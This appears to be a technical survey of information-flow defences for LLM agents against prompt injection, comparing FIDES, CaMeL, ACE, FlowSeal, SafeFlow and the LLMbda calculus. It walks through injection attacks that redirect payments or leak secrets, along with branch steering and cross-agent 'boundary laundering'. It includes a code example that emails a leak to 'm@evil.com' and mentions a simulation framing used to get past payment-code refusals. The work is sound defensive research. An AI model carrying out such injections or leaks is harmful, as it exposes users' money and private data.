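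The last row shows roughly how well a better model could do under these policies. In Banking and Slack, o1 is already close to that limit. In many banking tasks, the agent must read a file and follow the instructions in it, and the checks then block the payment, as the designers intended. A stronger model would probably handle variables better in Workspace and Travel, but no model can get a forbidden call past the policy. The limit is approximate because some data-dependent tasks succeed by luck. In one, the agent had to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. It judged the transaction by its large amount, which was trusted, and never read the untrusted subject line.

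### Labelling what a model writes

FIDES conservatively labels the planner's output with the join of all labels in the context. A model mistake cannot weaken this label, so the guarantee is deterministic once the source labels and the policy are fixed.

Siddiqui and colleagues proposed a less strict method in 2024, so that one outside e-mail doesn't affect the label on all later output. Their software looks for a subset of the messages in the context that would produce a similar answer, then has the model generate the answer again from that subset alone. If the software leaves out the invoice because it is irrelevant to a question about Ana's calendar, the new answer doesn't need the invoice's label. The model cannot copy text it never received, so the label is sound for direct copying even if the software chose the subset badly. An attacker may still have some influence over which messages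 the software keeps, because that choice can depend on untrusted text.

RTBAS, which Zhong and colleagues described in 2025, estimates which inputs influenced a model's output. It either measures attention, the weight the model gives to each earlier token, or asks a language model to judge which inputs mattered. Both methods can be wrong. A program can still provide a firm guarantee if it removes the inputs judged irrelevant and has the model answer without them. If it keeps those inputs and drops only their labels, a wrong estimate can cause output influenced by untrusted text to be labeled as trusted.

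*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FlowSeal, which tracks data at the level of tool calls. It is designed to keep a personal assistant from giving private records to people who ask for them cleverly. In one test, the attacker shares a document with a blank section for the assistant to fill in, and the assistant treats this as ordinary teamwork and writes down someone's medical history. A detailed prompt telling the model to obtain consent first didn't help much, and 52.2% of the sensitive items still leaked.

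FlowSeal keeps a register of private records. Code between the agent and its tools scans every result for those records and raises the context's label when it finds one. It then intercepts each outgoing message c to a destination d and allows it only if

ℓ(c) ⊑ ℓ(d), or declassify(c, d) = SAFE.

An unknown outsider has the lowest label, so once the agent has read a private record, the first condition fails for every message to that person. A separate language model, `declassify`, then reads the private records and the proposed message and decides whether the message is SAFE or BLOCKED. An attacker cannot make the agent skip this check, because code starts it every time. But the theorem that Shim and colleagues prove excludes cases where that model answers wrongly, so the guarantee is not deterministic.

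In the paper's tests, the model was rarely wrong. Leakage in the shared-document attack fell to 0.5%, and the agent completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defences. The paper's threat model excludes prompt injection, so these results are little evidence of how the defence would handle Ana's invoice. The paper also incorrectly describes FIDES as leaving policy enforcement to the language model, when ordinary code makes FIDES's checks.

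*SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026) uses models earlier in the process. It monitors groups of agents that divide up a task. For example, one agent may read a password file, another may rewrite the contents and a third may e-mail them out. A language model attaches labels from a fixed list, such as "credential access", and cites evidence for them. Code passes the labels from agent to agent and holds back irreversible actions until it has examined the whole path. A model's explanation can supply evidence for a label but cannot remove one.

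Dai and colleagues call this conditional determinism because the rules always give the same result once the models have produced their records. But if a model misses the password file, the rules may have nothing to act on. Across four benchmarks, the defence cut the average attack success rate from 69.3% to 12.7%, and the rate rose to 32.3% when the attackers added one of four jailbreaks (prompts written to defeat a model's safety training). Agents completed about 91% of harmless tasks on average, compared with 95% without the defence. The defence usefully reduces risk, whereas FIDES's rules would never allow a forbidden call on correctly labelled data.

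### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

Microsoft's documentation describes the Agent Framework version of FIDES as experimental and available only in Python. This version replaces the list of readers with three levels of confidentiality, which are public, private and user identity. The user identity level covers data such as passwords and personal details. Developers label the data that their tools return. They can also prevent a tool from running in an untrusted context, or set the highest level of confidentiality it may handle. By default, the framework hides untrusted results in variables and blocks calls that break a rule. Developers can configure it to ask a person for approval instead of blocking the call.

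Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes an attack on an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. A line in a public report tells the agent to read `.env`, a file of secret settings, and post its contents as a comment. The developer has turned off the feature that would hide this line from the model, so the model reads it and may obey it. If it does, the framework lets it read the file, but the file's private contents make the context private too. The comment tool accepts only public data, so the framework blocks the comment.

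Microsoft has given conflicting accounts of how the framework treats unlabelled data. In the May 2026 announcement, Microsoft wrote that the framework treats an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. In the documentation, Microsoft gives untrusted and public as the default for such a tool's output, but also describes the output as taking the join of its inputs' labels. An individual content item without a label counts as trusted and public. Developers who depend on any of these defaults need to test them on the installed version.

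Labeling data "untrusted and public" by default protects integrity but not confidentiality, although the documentation presents it as the safe choice. If the developer of Ana's assistant forgets to label her calendar tool, the calendar entries count as untrusted and public. A payment tool that refuses untrusted contexts will not act on them, but the assistant may send them to anyone.

Microsoft kept changing these details through the autumn. According to Releasebot's *Agent Framework Updates & Release Notes* (2026), a copy of Microsoft's notes, version 1.25.0 made FIDES stop when a tool's policy is invalid. Version 1.26.0, from 13 November, labels earlier messages conservatively when the program reloads them without a record of their origin. It also lets developers supply their own function for labelling messages from components such as memory.

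Labels are more useful if they stay attached to data when it passes from one company's tool to another's agent. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes prototypes that send labels through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. GitHub's MCP server can label content from public repositories as untrusted and public, and content from private ones as trusted and private. GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent, has an experimental mode that uses these labels. In this mode, an agent that has read both kinds of repository cannot post publicly, but it can work on either kind alone without interruption. Labeling everything in a private repository as trusted is a simplification, because an employee may have pasted in a stranger's bug report.

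Microsoft gives an example policy for sending messages in Microsoft Teams. The program sends the message if the context is trusted, because the decision to share then came from the user. It also sends the message if every member of the channel is already allowed to read the contents. Otherwise, it asks the user and names the people who would gain access.

These protections depend on the enforcing code being sound. Microsoft (2026) reported that on 17 November somebody uploaded two unauthorised versions of the framework's Python package, 1.26.1 and 1.26.2, containing code that steals credentials. PyPI, the public index that distributed them, no longer offers either version. Microsoft took the framework's code repository offline as a precaution and, as of 25 November, had no date for restoring access. FIDES could not have stopped the theft, because malicious code inside the package can read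 credentials without making a tool call.

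## Plans written as programs and run by a checking interpreter

FIDES calls its planner model again after every tool result, so text that the planner inspects can influence later steps. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) describes CaMeL, which prevents this. CaMeL's planner receives Ana's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a complete program for the task before anything reads her mail. CaMeL extends the dual-LLM pattern with tags on the data and a policy check before each tool call.

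### Ana's invoice as a program

The planner writes in a restricted form of Python, because language models already write Python well. For "Pay the invoice that came in today", it might produce this:

```python
mail = get_latest_email(subject="invoice")
bill = ask_quarantined_model(
    "Find the account number and the amount in cents.",
    mail,
    output_type=Bill,
)
send_payment(account=bill.account, amount_cents=bill.amount_cents)
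```

`Bill` is a record with two fields, a string of digits and an integer. The quarantined model must return a value of this type. As in the dual-LLM pattern, the planted line may change the account number the model returns but cannot add a step to the program. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this property control-flow integrity, meaning that the agent can make only the tool calls that a plan built from trusted information allows.

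Ordinary Python would run the program without checking where the account number came from. CaMeL therefore has its own interpreter. As Willison (2025) describes in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, it breaks the program into a tree of operations and works through them one by one. It records which earlier values each new value came from. The interpreter's language is small, and according to *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), programs in it cannot define their own functions or use recursion.

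The tag on a value lists its sources S and its permitted readers R. When the program combines two values, the result should get the tag

(S₁ ∪ S₂, R₁ ∩ R₂),

which keeps every source of either value and combines the readers as FIDES does. The tags in Ana's program look like this:

| Value | Contents | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| `"invoice"` | a search word the planner wrote | Ana's request | everyone |
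| `mail` | the invoice e-mail | outside sender | Ana, sender |
| `bill.account` | the thief's account number | outside sender, quarantined model | Ana, sender |
| `bill.amount_cents` | 40,000 | outside sender, quarantined model | Ana, sender |

Before each tool call, the interpreter applies a policy for that tool. In CaMeL, as Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, a policy is a Python function that inspects the tags on the arguments. A policy for payments could require that

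sources(`account`) ⊆ {Ana's request, Ana's supplier records}.

The sources of `bill.account` include the outside sender, so the interpreter refuses the payment or asks Ana to approve it. It would do the same if the account number were genuine. A policy for sending mail could check the recipients against the permitted readers, as FIDES does.

Having the quarantined model pick a supplier from Ana's records does not fully solve this. The e-mail determines which record the program opens, so a strict tracker would still list the sender as a source of the account number. A developer would have to make an exception for accounts on file.

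An ordinary agent can look at a tool's result and work out its structure, but CaMeL's planner writes the whole program, including the code that parses the results, before any tool runs. Developers must therefore document the exact format that every tool returns.

The arrangement improves privacy because the planner, and therefore the company that hosts it, never receives Ana's mail. Extracting values is easier than planning, so a smaller model on Ana's own computer might be able to do it.

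The CaMeL paper acknowledges that somebody has to write and maintain the policies, and that people who receive too many approval requests start accepting all of them. Willison shares the concern, writing that he has trouble reasoning through such policies himself, even after two decades of work on application security.

### CaMeL's results on AgentDojo

Narisetty and colleagues cite CaMeL's original results for OpenAI's o3 model with attacks present. CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as the undefended agent. No attack covered by CaMeL's threat model succeeded.

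*The LLMbda Calculus* describes the two attacks that AgentDojo still counted as successes. In one, the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. CaMeL's designers place this case outside their threat model, though the user would still lose money. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark's text search found the attacker's sentence in the answer, so this success is mostly an artefact of the scoring.

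As with most published results for such systems, the attacks were older than the defence, and nobody had revised them to get past CaMeL's policies.

*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands) reran CaMeL on the Banking suite with two newer models, repeating each of the 16 tasks three times. The second column shows how many tasks CaMeL completed without an attack. The last column covers only the attacked runs that finished.

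| Model and setting | Tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2, policies off | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| GPT-5.2, policies on | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| MiMo-v2.5, policies off | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5, policies on | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

The policies roughly halved the number of completed tasks and stopped only a handful of attacks. They may be more useful than this suggests, because they had few attacks to stop. In 97 of the suite's 144 pairs of task and attack, the attacker needs a tool call or file read that a plan written for the user's task would never contain, so fixing the plan in advance is normally enough. In the other 47, the plan already contains the calls the attacker needs, so a false value could be enough for the attack to succeed. Yet with the policies off, the attack succeeded in only 3 of 282 such runs. AgentDojo's attacks are mostly written as instructions,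 and they seldom tricked the quarantined model into returning the value the attacker wanted. An attack that just put a different account number on Ana's invoice would be a much harder test of the policies.

The 37.5% is consistent with the 77% for AgentDojo as a whole, because Banking has an unusually large share of tasks that depend on untrusted text. FIDES lost many of the same tasks.

### Plans that ignore which apps are installed

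CaMeL's planner reads the tool descriptions and treats them as trusted. This is reasonable if Ana's employer wrote the tools, but less so if she installs apps made by strangers. *ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues) demonstrates the danger on IsolateGPT, an earlier system that runs each app in isolation. In its example, a user asks for the fare between two streets, which two apps, MetroHail and QuickRide, can calculate. QuickRide's description contains an instruction to leave MetroHail out. The planner follows this instruction, so the user sees only QuickRide's price.

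ACE, presented at the NDSS security symposium in February 2026, hides the installed apps from the planner. It is named for its three stages: abstract, concrete and execute. In the abstract stage, a model receives the user's request and, optionally, a trusted note about the setting. It invents the apps it needs, each with a name, a description and types for its inputs and outputs, and writes a program that uses them. For Ana's request, it might invent `InvoiceReader` and `PaymentSender`.

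In the concrete stage, software matches the invented apps to real ones. For each invented app, it first discards installed apps whose descriptions are too different. A model then judges, one pair at a time, whether an installed app can do the invented app's job. Because each judgement involves only one installed app, QuickRide's description cannot affect the judgement of MetroHail. If the inputs or outputs don't match, the model also supplies a small adapter.

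ACE then checks the matched program without running it. Every app has a clearance, such as "personal" or "financial", and every variable has a label. Li and colleagues illustrate the difficulty with a loop:

```python
a = ""
for i in range(4):
    network_send(a)
    a = load_bank_details()
```

The first pass through the loop sends an empty string, which is harmless. By the end of that pass, `a` contains bank details, which the second pass would send. ACE recalculates the labels for the loop until they stop changing, finds that `network_send` would receive financial data, and rejects the plan.

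For an `if` statement, ACE adds the condition's label to every variable that either branch assigns. ACE checks the plan before running it, so the check can cover both branches, whereas CaMeL's tracking at run time can miss the effect of a branch that the program skips. If one choice of apps fails the check, ACE can try another, and it stops with an error if none passes.

Each app runs in its own container with only the permissions it needs, and ordinary code checks the type of every result. In one test with two ride-hailing apps, QuickRide returned an instruction to misreport MetroHail's fare. The plan required a number, so the user saw MetroHail's real fare and a type error for QuickRide. The check would have accepted a false number, so QuickRide could still have lied about its own fare.

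Li and colleagues tested ACE on the 1,054 cases of InjecAgent, a benchmark of planted instructions, and the attacker's app never ran. The score measures only whether that app runs, so the result follows almost directly from fixing the plan in advance. The agent used the right app in 60% to 85% of cases, depending on the models. With GPT-4o, ACE found a suitable match in 84.3% of cases, and 99.1% of those then ran without error, so most of the failures with GPT-4o came from planning without knowing which apps were installed.

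ACE did well on harder tasks that required several steps. With GPT-4.1, it correctly answered 85.7% of questions about a small database. The average cost per request rose from about $0.01 with one tool to $0.27 with 26, because a model may have to compare every invented app with every installed one. Li and colleagues could not formally prove that the static check catches every leak, because Python's behaviour is too complex.

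### When the plan depends on what the agent finds

If Ana types, "Do the things Ben asked for in his last e-mail," no planner can write the steps without reading the e-mail, and reading it would lose the protection. Foerster and colleagues call this a fundamental limitation of separating planning from data.

A planner can get around the limitation in a way that defeats its purpose. In one Banking task, the agent is told to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. In the reruns of CaMeL, the planner sometimes wrote a loop that took each instruction from the file and called the matching tool, with a branch for every tool. The plan was fixed, but text in the file could trigger any tool. With the policies off, two attacks succeeded this way. Control-flow integrity therefore protects Ana only if the plan limits which actions the file can trigger.

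In other tasks, the need for an extra step becomes clear only after a tool returns its result. An ordinary agent can add the step, but CaMeL can follow only the paths in its program. Peters-Gill and colleagues traced most of CaMeL's failures on harmless tasks to this limit. They also saw programs continue with the wrong data. An agent would request readings for one machine and period, and the agent supplying them would find none and return readings for a nearby period. The program, written in advance, would not check that the period matched.

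The planner can add branches for situations it can predict. AgentDojo requires little of this. Foerster and colleagues found that CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo's tasks averaged 52 lines and about five tool calls, and that 79% of the branches depended only on the program's own values, such as loop counters.

### Plans for a screen the planner cannot see

Computer-use agents are a much harder case because they choose each click and keystroke by looking at a screenshot. A CaMeL planner would have to write all these actions without seeing the screen.

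Foerster and colleagues made this workable with a planning method called NOVA. They instruct the planner to build every step from three parts. First, a quarantined vision model describes the screen. The function `verify_hypothesis` then uses a quarantined model to compare the description with a prediction, such as "a cookie banner is visible". Finally, the interpreter uses the verdict to choose a branch, which contains the click. The plans averaged 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, and about half the steps were fallbacks that a given run never used.

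The researchers tested NOVA on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in real desktop programs. They used 60 tasks that the small open model UI-TARS could complete without protection. Within three attempts, CaMeL completed 18.3% of them without NOVA and 58.3% with it. On a single attempt, CaMeL with NOVA completed 41.7%.

The paper's headline figures make the method look better than it is because they count extra attempts, which help only if something can recognise which attempt worked. The paper reports a 19% improvement over unprotected UI-TARS on the full benchmark, but the protected agent had three attempts at each task and the unprotected agent had one. With one attempt each, on the 339 tasks that the benchmark can check automatically, the protected agent completed 15.0% and the unprotected one 17.7%. For the larger Claude Sonnet 4.5, the reported 57% is the share of tasks solved within five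 attempts, out of those that Claude had solved unprotected. With one attempt, the share was 28.4%.

FIDES can use the same method, but its planner chooses one step at a time and normally cannot see stored answers. Foerster and colleagues let the planner see true-or-false answers. They also limited how often it could query the same variable, because repeated questions could reveal the whole screen. On the 60 tasks, FIDES completed 33.3% on one attempt and 66.7% within five, compared with 41.7% and 65.0% for CaMeL.

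The costs differed far more. The table gives totals for 17 tasks, with five attempts per task for the protected agents.

| | No defence | CaMeL | FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input tokens | 1,797,736 | 2,950,253 | 51,724,263 |
| Output tokens | 13,120 | 456,105 | 1,874,795 |
| All tokens, relative to no defence | 1 | 1.88 | 29.6 |
| Charges for commercial models | none | $5.40 | $76.07 |

FIDES resends the full history to its planner at every step, whereas CaMeL's planner writes each plan in one go. CaMeL's total is modest, but its output tokens rise 35-fold, mainly because the plans are long. The undefended agent ran entirely on a local model, so it incurred no charges.

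### Steering the agent down a planned branch

An attacker who cannot add a branch to a plan may still be able to choose which of its existing branches runs. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In their main example, the attacker buys an advert that looks like a cookie notice. Nearly every plan for browsing the web includes a step that finds the cookie notice and accepts it. The vision model returns the position of the fake button, and the program, still following its plan, clicks it, which opens the attacker's site.

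A data policy can stop a bad payment because `send_payment(account, amount)` always means the same thing, but `click(x, y)` may open a menu or confirm a transfer, depending on the screen. The researchers therefore ran CaMeL without data policies and tried other checks. One compared each click with the page's underlying structure and flagged 6 of 10 fake notices in ordinary image adverts. It failed on adverts that carry their own HTML, but with a second vision model added, the system flagged 5 of 10 of those. Each set-up also raised false alarms on 3 or 4 of 17 harmless tasks.

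In another attack, which the checks missed, the researchers altered the pixels of a banner on a medicines website. UI-TARS then clicked a particular drug instead of the natural products database the user wanted, and generated a plausible reason for the click.

An attacker can send the browser to a hostile site with one false answer from the vision model, but stealing a payment remains difficult. The task must already include a payment, and the attacker needs at least two false answers that fit together, such as the recipient and the position of the confirm button.

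### Several agents that call one another

Companies often divide work among agents. An orchestrator calls specialised agents as if they were tools, and each treats the orchestrator's message as its user's request. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that giving every agent its own CaMeL does not protect the group.

In a test by Peters-Gill and colleagues, the user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack, a workplace chat service. One agent reads the applicant database, where an attacker has planted an instruction to send the data to an outside address. The orchestrator's planner never receives that instruction, but its program pastes the summary into a message to the notification agent, whose planner treats the whole message as a trusted request. The notification agent's planner then writes a program with two steps, one for Julie and one for the attacker. The researchers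 call this boundary laundering, because untrusted text becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to another.

Ana's assistant would have the same fault if it handed invoices to a payment agent with a message such as `f"Pay this: {mail}"`. The researchers' repair, multi-CaMeL, separates instructions from data:

```python
payment_agent(
    message="Pay the invoice using the details provided.",
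    variables={"account": bill.account,
               "amount_cents": bill.amount_cents},
)
```

The payment agent's planner reads the message but not the contents of the variables. The interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output. The tags stay attached to the variables, so a payment policy could still block a payment to the thief's account.

Peters-Gill and colleagues divided AgentDojo's tools among several agents and ran 949 attack cases on each of five models. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded with no defence, 0.2% when each agent had its own CaMeL, and none with multi-CaMeL. All the attacks that got past the separate CaMeLs involved boundary laundering. Two older models, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, account for nearly all the attacks that succeeded with no defence. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without a defence, so these fixed attacks cannot show what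 multi-CaMeL adds for that model.

Applying CaMeL to each agent lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points on 112 tasks from AssetOpsBench, a benchmark about industrial equipment. Separating instructions from data lowered it by another 3.2 points. For the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the losses were 13.4 and 0.85 points.

These tests also ran without data policies, and an attacker can still influence which branch a program takes. Suppose Ana asks her assistant to pay the invoice now if it is overdue and otherwise to set a reminder. The program calls either the payment agent or the calendar agent, depending on the due date in the e-mail. An attacker who changes the date can trigger an early payment without adding anything to the plan. With policies on, CaMeL's interpreter can count the e-mail as a source of any call inside the branch. A strict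 payment policy would then block the early payment, but it would also block payment of an invoice that really was overdue.

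## Information flows that tracking misses, and a proved interpreter

CaMeL's interpreter can count the sources of a branch's condition as sources of any tool call inside that branch. But a program can also leak a secret by skipping a line, and an interpreter that tracks only the lines it runs will miss the leak.

### Secrets in skipped lines

Denning illustrated the problem with the statement `if a = 0 then b := 0`. If b starts at 1, it becomes 0 when a is 0 and stays 1 otherwise. Anyone who can read b therefore learns whether a was 0, even if the assignment never ran. Denning called this an implicit flow, unlike the explicit flow in `b := a`, which copies the data.

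Her paper also describes an early remedy, J. S. Fenton's Data Mark Machine, an abstract computer that labels the program counter, which records the instruction that runs next. When the program enters a branch, the machine joins the condition's label to the program counter's label, and it restores the old label when the program leaves. Inside a branch that depends on a secret, the program may write only to secret variables. Fenton proved that this is enough if every variable has a fixed label. If b is public and a is secret, the machine does not run `b := 0`, so b stays at 1 whatever the value of a.

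In CaMeL, the label belongs to the value, so a variable can be public on one line and secret on the next. This reopens the gap. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (a paper that also goes by the title *The LLMbda Calculus*), adapt a classic counterexample of Fenton's to an agent that can read a bank balance. In outline, the program is:

```python
tmp = True
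rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is secret, and the other variables start out public.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| First `if` | runs; `tmp` becomes False and secret | skipped; `tmp` stays True and public |
| Second `if` | skipped; `rich` stays True and public | runs; `rich` becomes False and stays public |
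| Third `if` | sends the e-mail | sends nothing |

CaMeL would block an e-mail sent from inside the conditional that tests the balance. Here it allows the e-mail because `rich` is labeled public. CaMeL raises a variable's label only when it runs an assignment to that variable, and in the first column it never runs `rich = False`.

ACE avoids this mistake by examining both branches before the program runs. A monitor that sees only the lines that run has to be stricter. One known method, the no-sensitive-upgrade check, allows an assignment to a variable x only if

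pc ⊑ ℓ(x),

where pc is the program counter's label and ℓ(x) is the label x already had. In the example, the check stops the program at `tmp = False`, because pc is secret and `tmp` is public.

The check also stops harmless programs, including some that never use the variable again. Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, call such a variable "partially leaked". Their alternative allows the assignment, marks the variable and stops the program only if it later branches on that variable. Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues (2015), in *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, extended the method from two labels to any lattice of labels.

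An attacker cannot get the bank-balance program into CaMeL by putting it in an e-mail, because the planner writes its program before anything reads the e-mail. The leak requires a planner that writes such code by accident or works against the user.

### Leaks that add up over retries

Stopping the program also reveals information. If a check stops it only when the balance is above the threshold, anyone who notices that it stopped learns one bit about the balance. Most information-flow systems tolerate a leak of this size.

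In CaMeL, a planner can repeat this leak. CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop, which requests another program from the planner when one fails. Garby and colleagues point out that this loop has no labels, so each new program starts with no recorded dependencies, even though it depends on whether the policy blocked the last one. Suppose that Ana's balance is between 0 and 1,048,575 cents. A hostile planner could halve the range with each attempt by testing whether the balance is in the upper half. Since 2²⁰ = 1,048,576, 20 attempts would reveal the exact balance. CaMeL censors the error messages that go back to the planner, which reduces the leak but comes with no formal guarantee.

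The researchers also found an ordinary bug. When a CaMeL program inserted an untrusted value into literal text, the interpreter treated the value as trusted. An account number from Ana's invoice could lose its label this way.

They attribute these faults to incomplete tracking rather than carelessness. In their view, a guarantee covers only the information flows that are tracked, and tracking rarely covers them all. The boundary laundering that Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated, in which one agent's data becomes another agent's instructions, also happens where tracking stops.

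### A language in which conversations have labels

Garby and colleagues address this with the LLMbda calculus, a small programming language with exact rules for what every program does. It extends the lambda calculus, a theoretical language of functions. Every value has a label. The conversation with the model also has one, which is the join of the labels of all the messages the program has sent in it.

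Four operations act on the conversation:

- `send` adds a message and joins the message's label to the conversation's label.
- `recv` gets the model's reply, parses it as code and runs it, with the program counter at the conversation's label.
- `fork` runs an expression on a copy of the conversation, then discards the copy and keeps the result.
- `clear` empties the conversation and resets its label to that of the program counter.

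In FIDES and CaMeL, the quarantined model is a fixed part of the architecture. Here a programmer can write one in a line. In simplified form, with `@` standing for `send` followed by `recv`, it is:

```
let quarantine = \prompt. fork (let _ = clear in @prompt)
```

Suppose Ana's assistant passes her invoice to this function and asks for the account number. The program copies the conversation, empties the copy and sends the invoice, which makes the copy's label untrusted. The reply is untrusted too. When `fork` ends, the original conversation returns with its trusted label, and only the account number remains untrusted.

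One of the paper's examples leaves out `clear`. The program explains the format of British postcodes to the model once, then forks the conversation for each of three addresses. Every fork starts with the explanation, and none contains the other addresses.

The no-sensitive-upgrade check also applies to conversations. In another example, a program tells the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set x to true. Finally, the program asks the model for x. The interpreter blocks the second message because it would make the contents of a public conversation depend on a secret.

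### Endorsement

Ana may want her assistant to act on something it learned from an untrusted e-mail. The calculus allows this with an operation called `endorse`, which raises a value's integrity label. In the paper's example, a quarantined model sorts an e-mail into one of a few fixed categories, and the program endorses the category so it can be used as the subject of a reply.

FIDES's policy can also let through an untrusted value from a small set. Garby and colleagues argue that nobody can tell from a given run whether this was the intended exception or a leak. Each `endorse`, however, appears in the program's text, so a reviewer can find it and ask whether it is justified.

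Endorsing a secret password leaves it secret. An endorsed value also can't be more trusted than the program counter, so an `endorse` in code derived from an untrusted e-mail has no effect.

That last protection fails if the program endorsed the e-mail first, because code derived from the e-mail would then run as trusted. The researchers describe an optional wrapper that marks every endorsed value and refuses to endorse a marked value again. Another wrapper endorses only values from a fixed list of n values, so an attacker should gain at most log₂ n bits from each endorsement. The researchers have not yet proved a bound for this wrapper.

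### What the theorem says

The central result is termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, or TIPNI. Like other forms of noninterference, it compares two starting points that differ only in data, such as Ana's balance, that is hidden from some observer. Because a language model's replies are random, it must compare the probabilities of what the observer sees. "Termination-insensitive" means that hidden data may still affect whether the program finishes.

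In symbols, let m be the highest label the observer can read. Write C for a conversation, e for a program, and ∼_m for "looks the same at level m". Let ⟦C, e⟧_m be the probabilities of the final results as the observer sees them. These may add up to less than 1, and the shortfall is the probability that the program never finishes or that a check stops it. The theorem states that for every m,

if C₀ ∼_m C₁ and e₀ ∼_m e₁, then ⟦C₀, e₀⟧_m ⌣ ⟦C₁, e₁⟧_m.

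Two sets of probabilities μ and ν are compatible, written μ ⌣ ν, if some third set ω gives every result a probability at least as large as both μ and ν do, and the probabilities in ω add up to at most 1.

Suppose an outsider can see only whether the assistant answers yes or no. With a low balance, each answer has probability 0.5. With a high balance, yes has probability 0.5, no has 0.3, and the program stops without answering in the remaining 0.2 of cases. These two distributions are compatible, since ω can assign 0.5 to each answer. The theorem rules out a high balance that instead gives 0.7 for yes and 0.3 for no, because ω would have to assign at least 0.7 to yes and 0.5 to no, and their sum of 1.2 exceeds 1.

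It also limits how much the exception can leak. If div(μ) is the probability that a run fails to finish, then

½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)| ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2,

where the sum runs over every result q that the observer can distinguish. In the permitted example both sides equal 0.1. For programs that always finish, the right-hand side is zero and the probabilities must be identical.

To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues construct ω from a second, imaginary way of running the program. When a label rises above m, this version skips the computation and returns an empty value. It never uses the hidden data, so both starting points give the same ω. This version also reaches each visible result at least as often as the real program does.

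The theorem covers every program in the language, including code that the model writes during a run. It also covers choices between actions, which FIDES's theorem does not cover. If the assistant contacts a taxi firm only when Ana's secret calendar shows a trip, the message gets the calendar's label from the program counter, and a policy can block it.

A second theorem shows that the guarantee for secrets still holds in programs that use `endorse`. Neither an endorsement nor an attacker's choice of untrusted input can make a secret affect a public result, apart from the exception for stopping. The integrity guarantee is necessarily weaker in these programs, because endorsement exists to override it.

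Both theorems depend on developers labelling the sources correctly and putting the right checks in front of the tools. They treat all data sources as part of the program, but real mailboxes and banks are outside it. They also cover only a single run, so someone who kept restarting a stopped program from outside could bring back CaMeL's retry leak.

### The proved interpreter

A proof about a language may not hold for an agent if the software that runs the agent departs from the language's rules. CaMeL's rules are defined only in its Python code. Garby and colleagues wrote their definitions, proofs and interpreter in Lean, a programming language whose core checks proofs mechanically.

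The interpreter gets the reply to each request from a function called an oracle. In the proofs, the oracle is a random table of replies, while in real use it sends the conversation to a model over the network. A third theorem states that running the interpreter with a randomly drawn table gives exactly the probabilities that appear in TIPNI. For example, if a program asks the model twice to flip a coin that lands heads 30% of the time, both calculations give 0.49 for no heads, 0.42 for one and 0.09 for two.

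As far as the researchers know, this is the first program for running agents with such proofs about its own executable code. The proofs assume that the model draws each reply independently from a fixed distribution, and they do not cover the code that makes the network request. *PerMIT* (2026) uses Lean to give machine-checked proofs about the integrity of an agent's persistent memory.

### RANDORI on the Banking suite

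To test whether an agent can do useful work under these rules, Garby and colleagues wrote one called RANDORI in the calculus. Like CaMeL, it has a planner that writes a program before seeing any untrusted data. If the planner retried programs on real data, the first error caused by that data would taint every later attempt. RANDORI therefore practises on made-up data, with payment tools that do nothing and files that contain only a placeholder. Once a program works, the planner writes a final version, which may include `endorse` and runs on the real account.

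The researchers ran each of AgentDojo's 16 Banking tasks three times. The table shows the share completed with no attack present.

| Model | RANDORI | RANDORI without `endorse` | CaMeL, policies off | CaMeL, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | not reported | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 62.5% | not reported | not reported |
| MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 54.2% | 70.8% | 37.5% |

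RANDORI always enforces its policies, yet it completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without any. The margins of error are around 20 percentage points, so small differences in the table mean little. The gap between RANDORI and CaMeL with policies is larger, but RANDORI uses only some of CaMeL's policies, in a looser form. Its policy for scheduling a payment, for instance, requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. The looser policies probably explain part of the gap, since RANDORI stayed ahead even without `endorse`. The prompt told the models that they were in a simulation with no real money, because they often refused to write payment code otherwise.

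RANDORI resisted attacks in all but two of 1,296 runs across the three models. This is limited evidence of its security, because AgentDojo's fixed attacks rarely succeeded against CaMeL's plans even with the policies off.

Both successful attacks on RANDORI involved the same task, run with GPT-5.2. The attacker had replaced the file that describes a payment, as in one of the attacks that beat CaMeL in its original tests. The planner endorsed the details from the file, and the money went to the attacker. Without `endorse`, RANDORI blocks the attack but also can't pay a genuine bill from a file.

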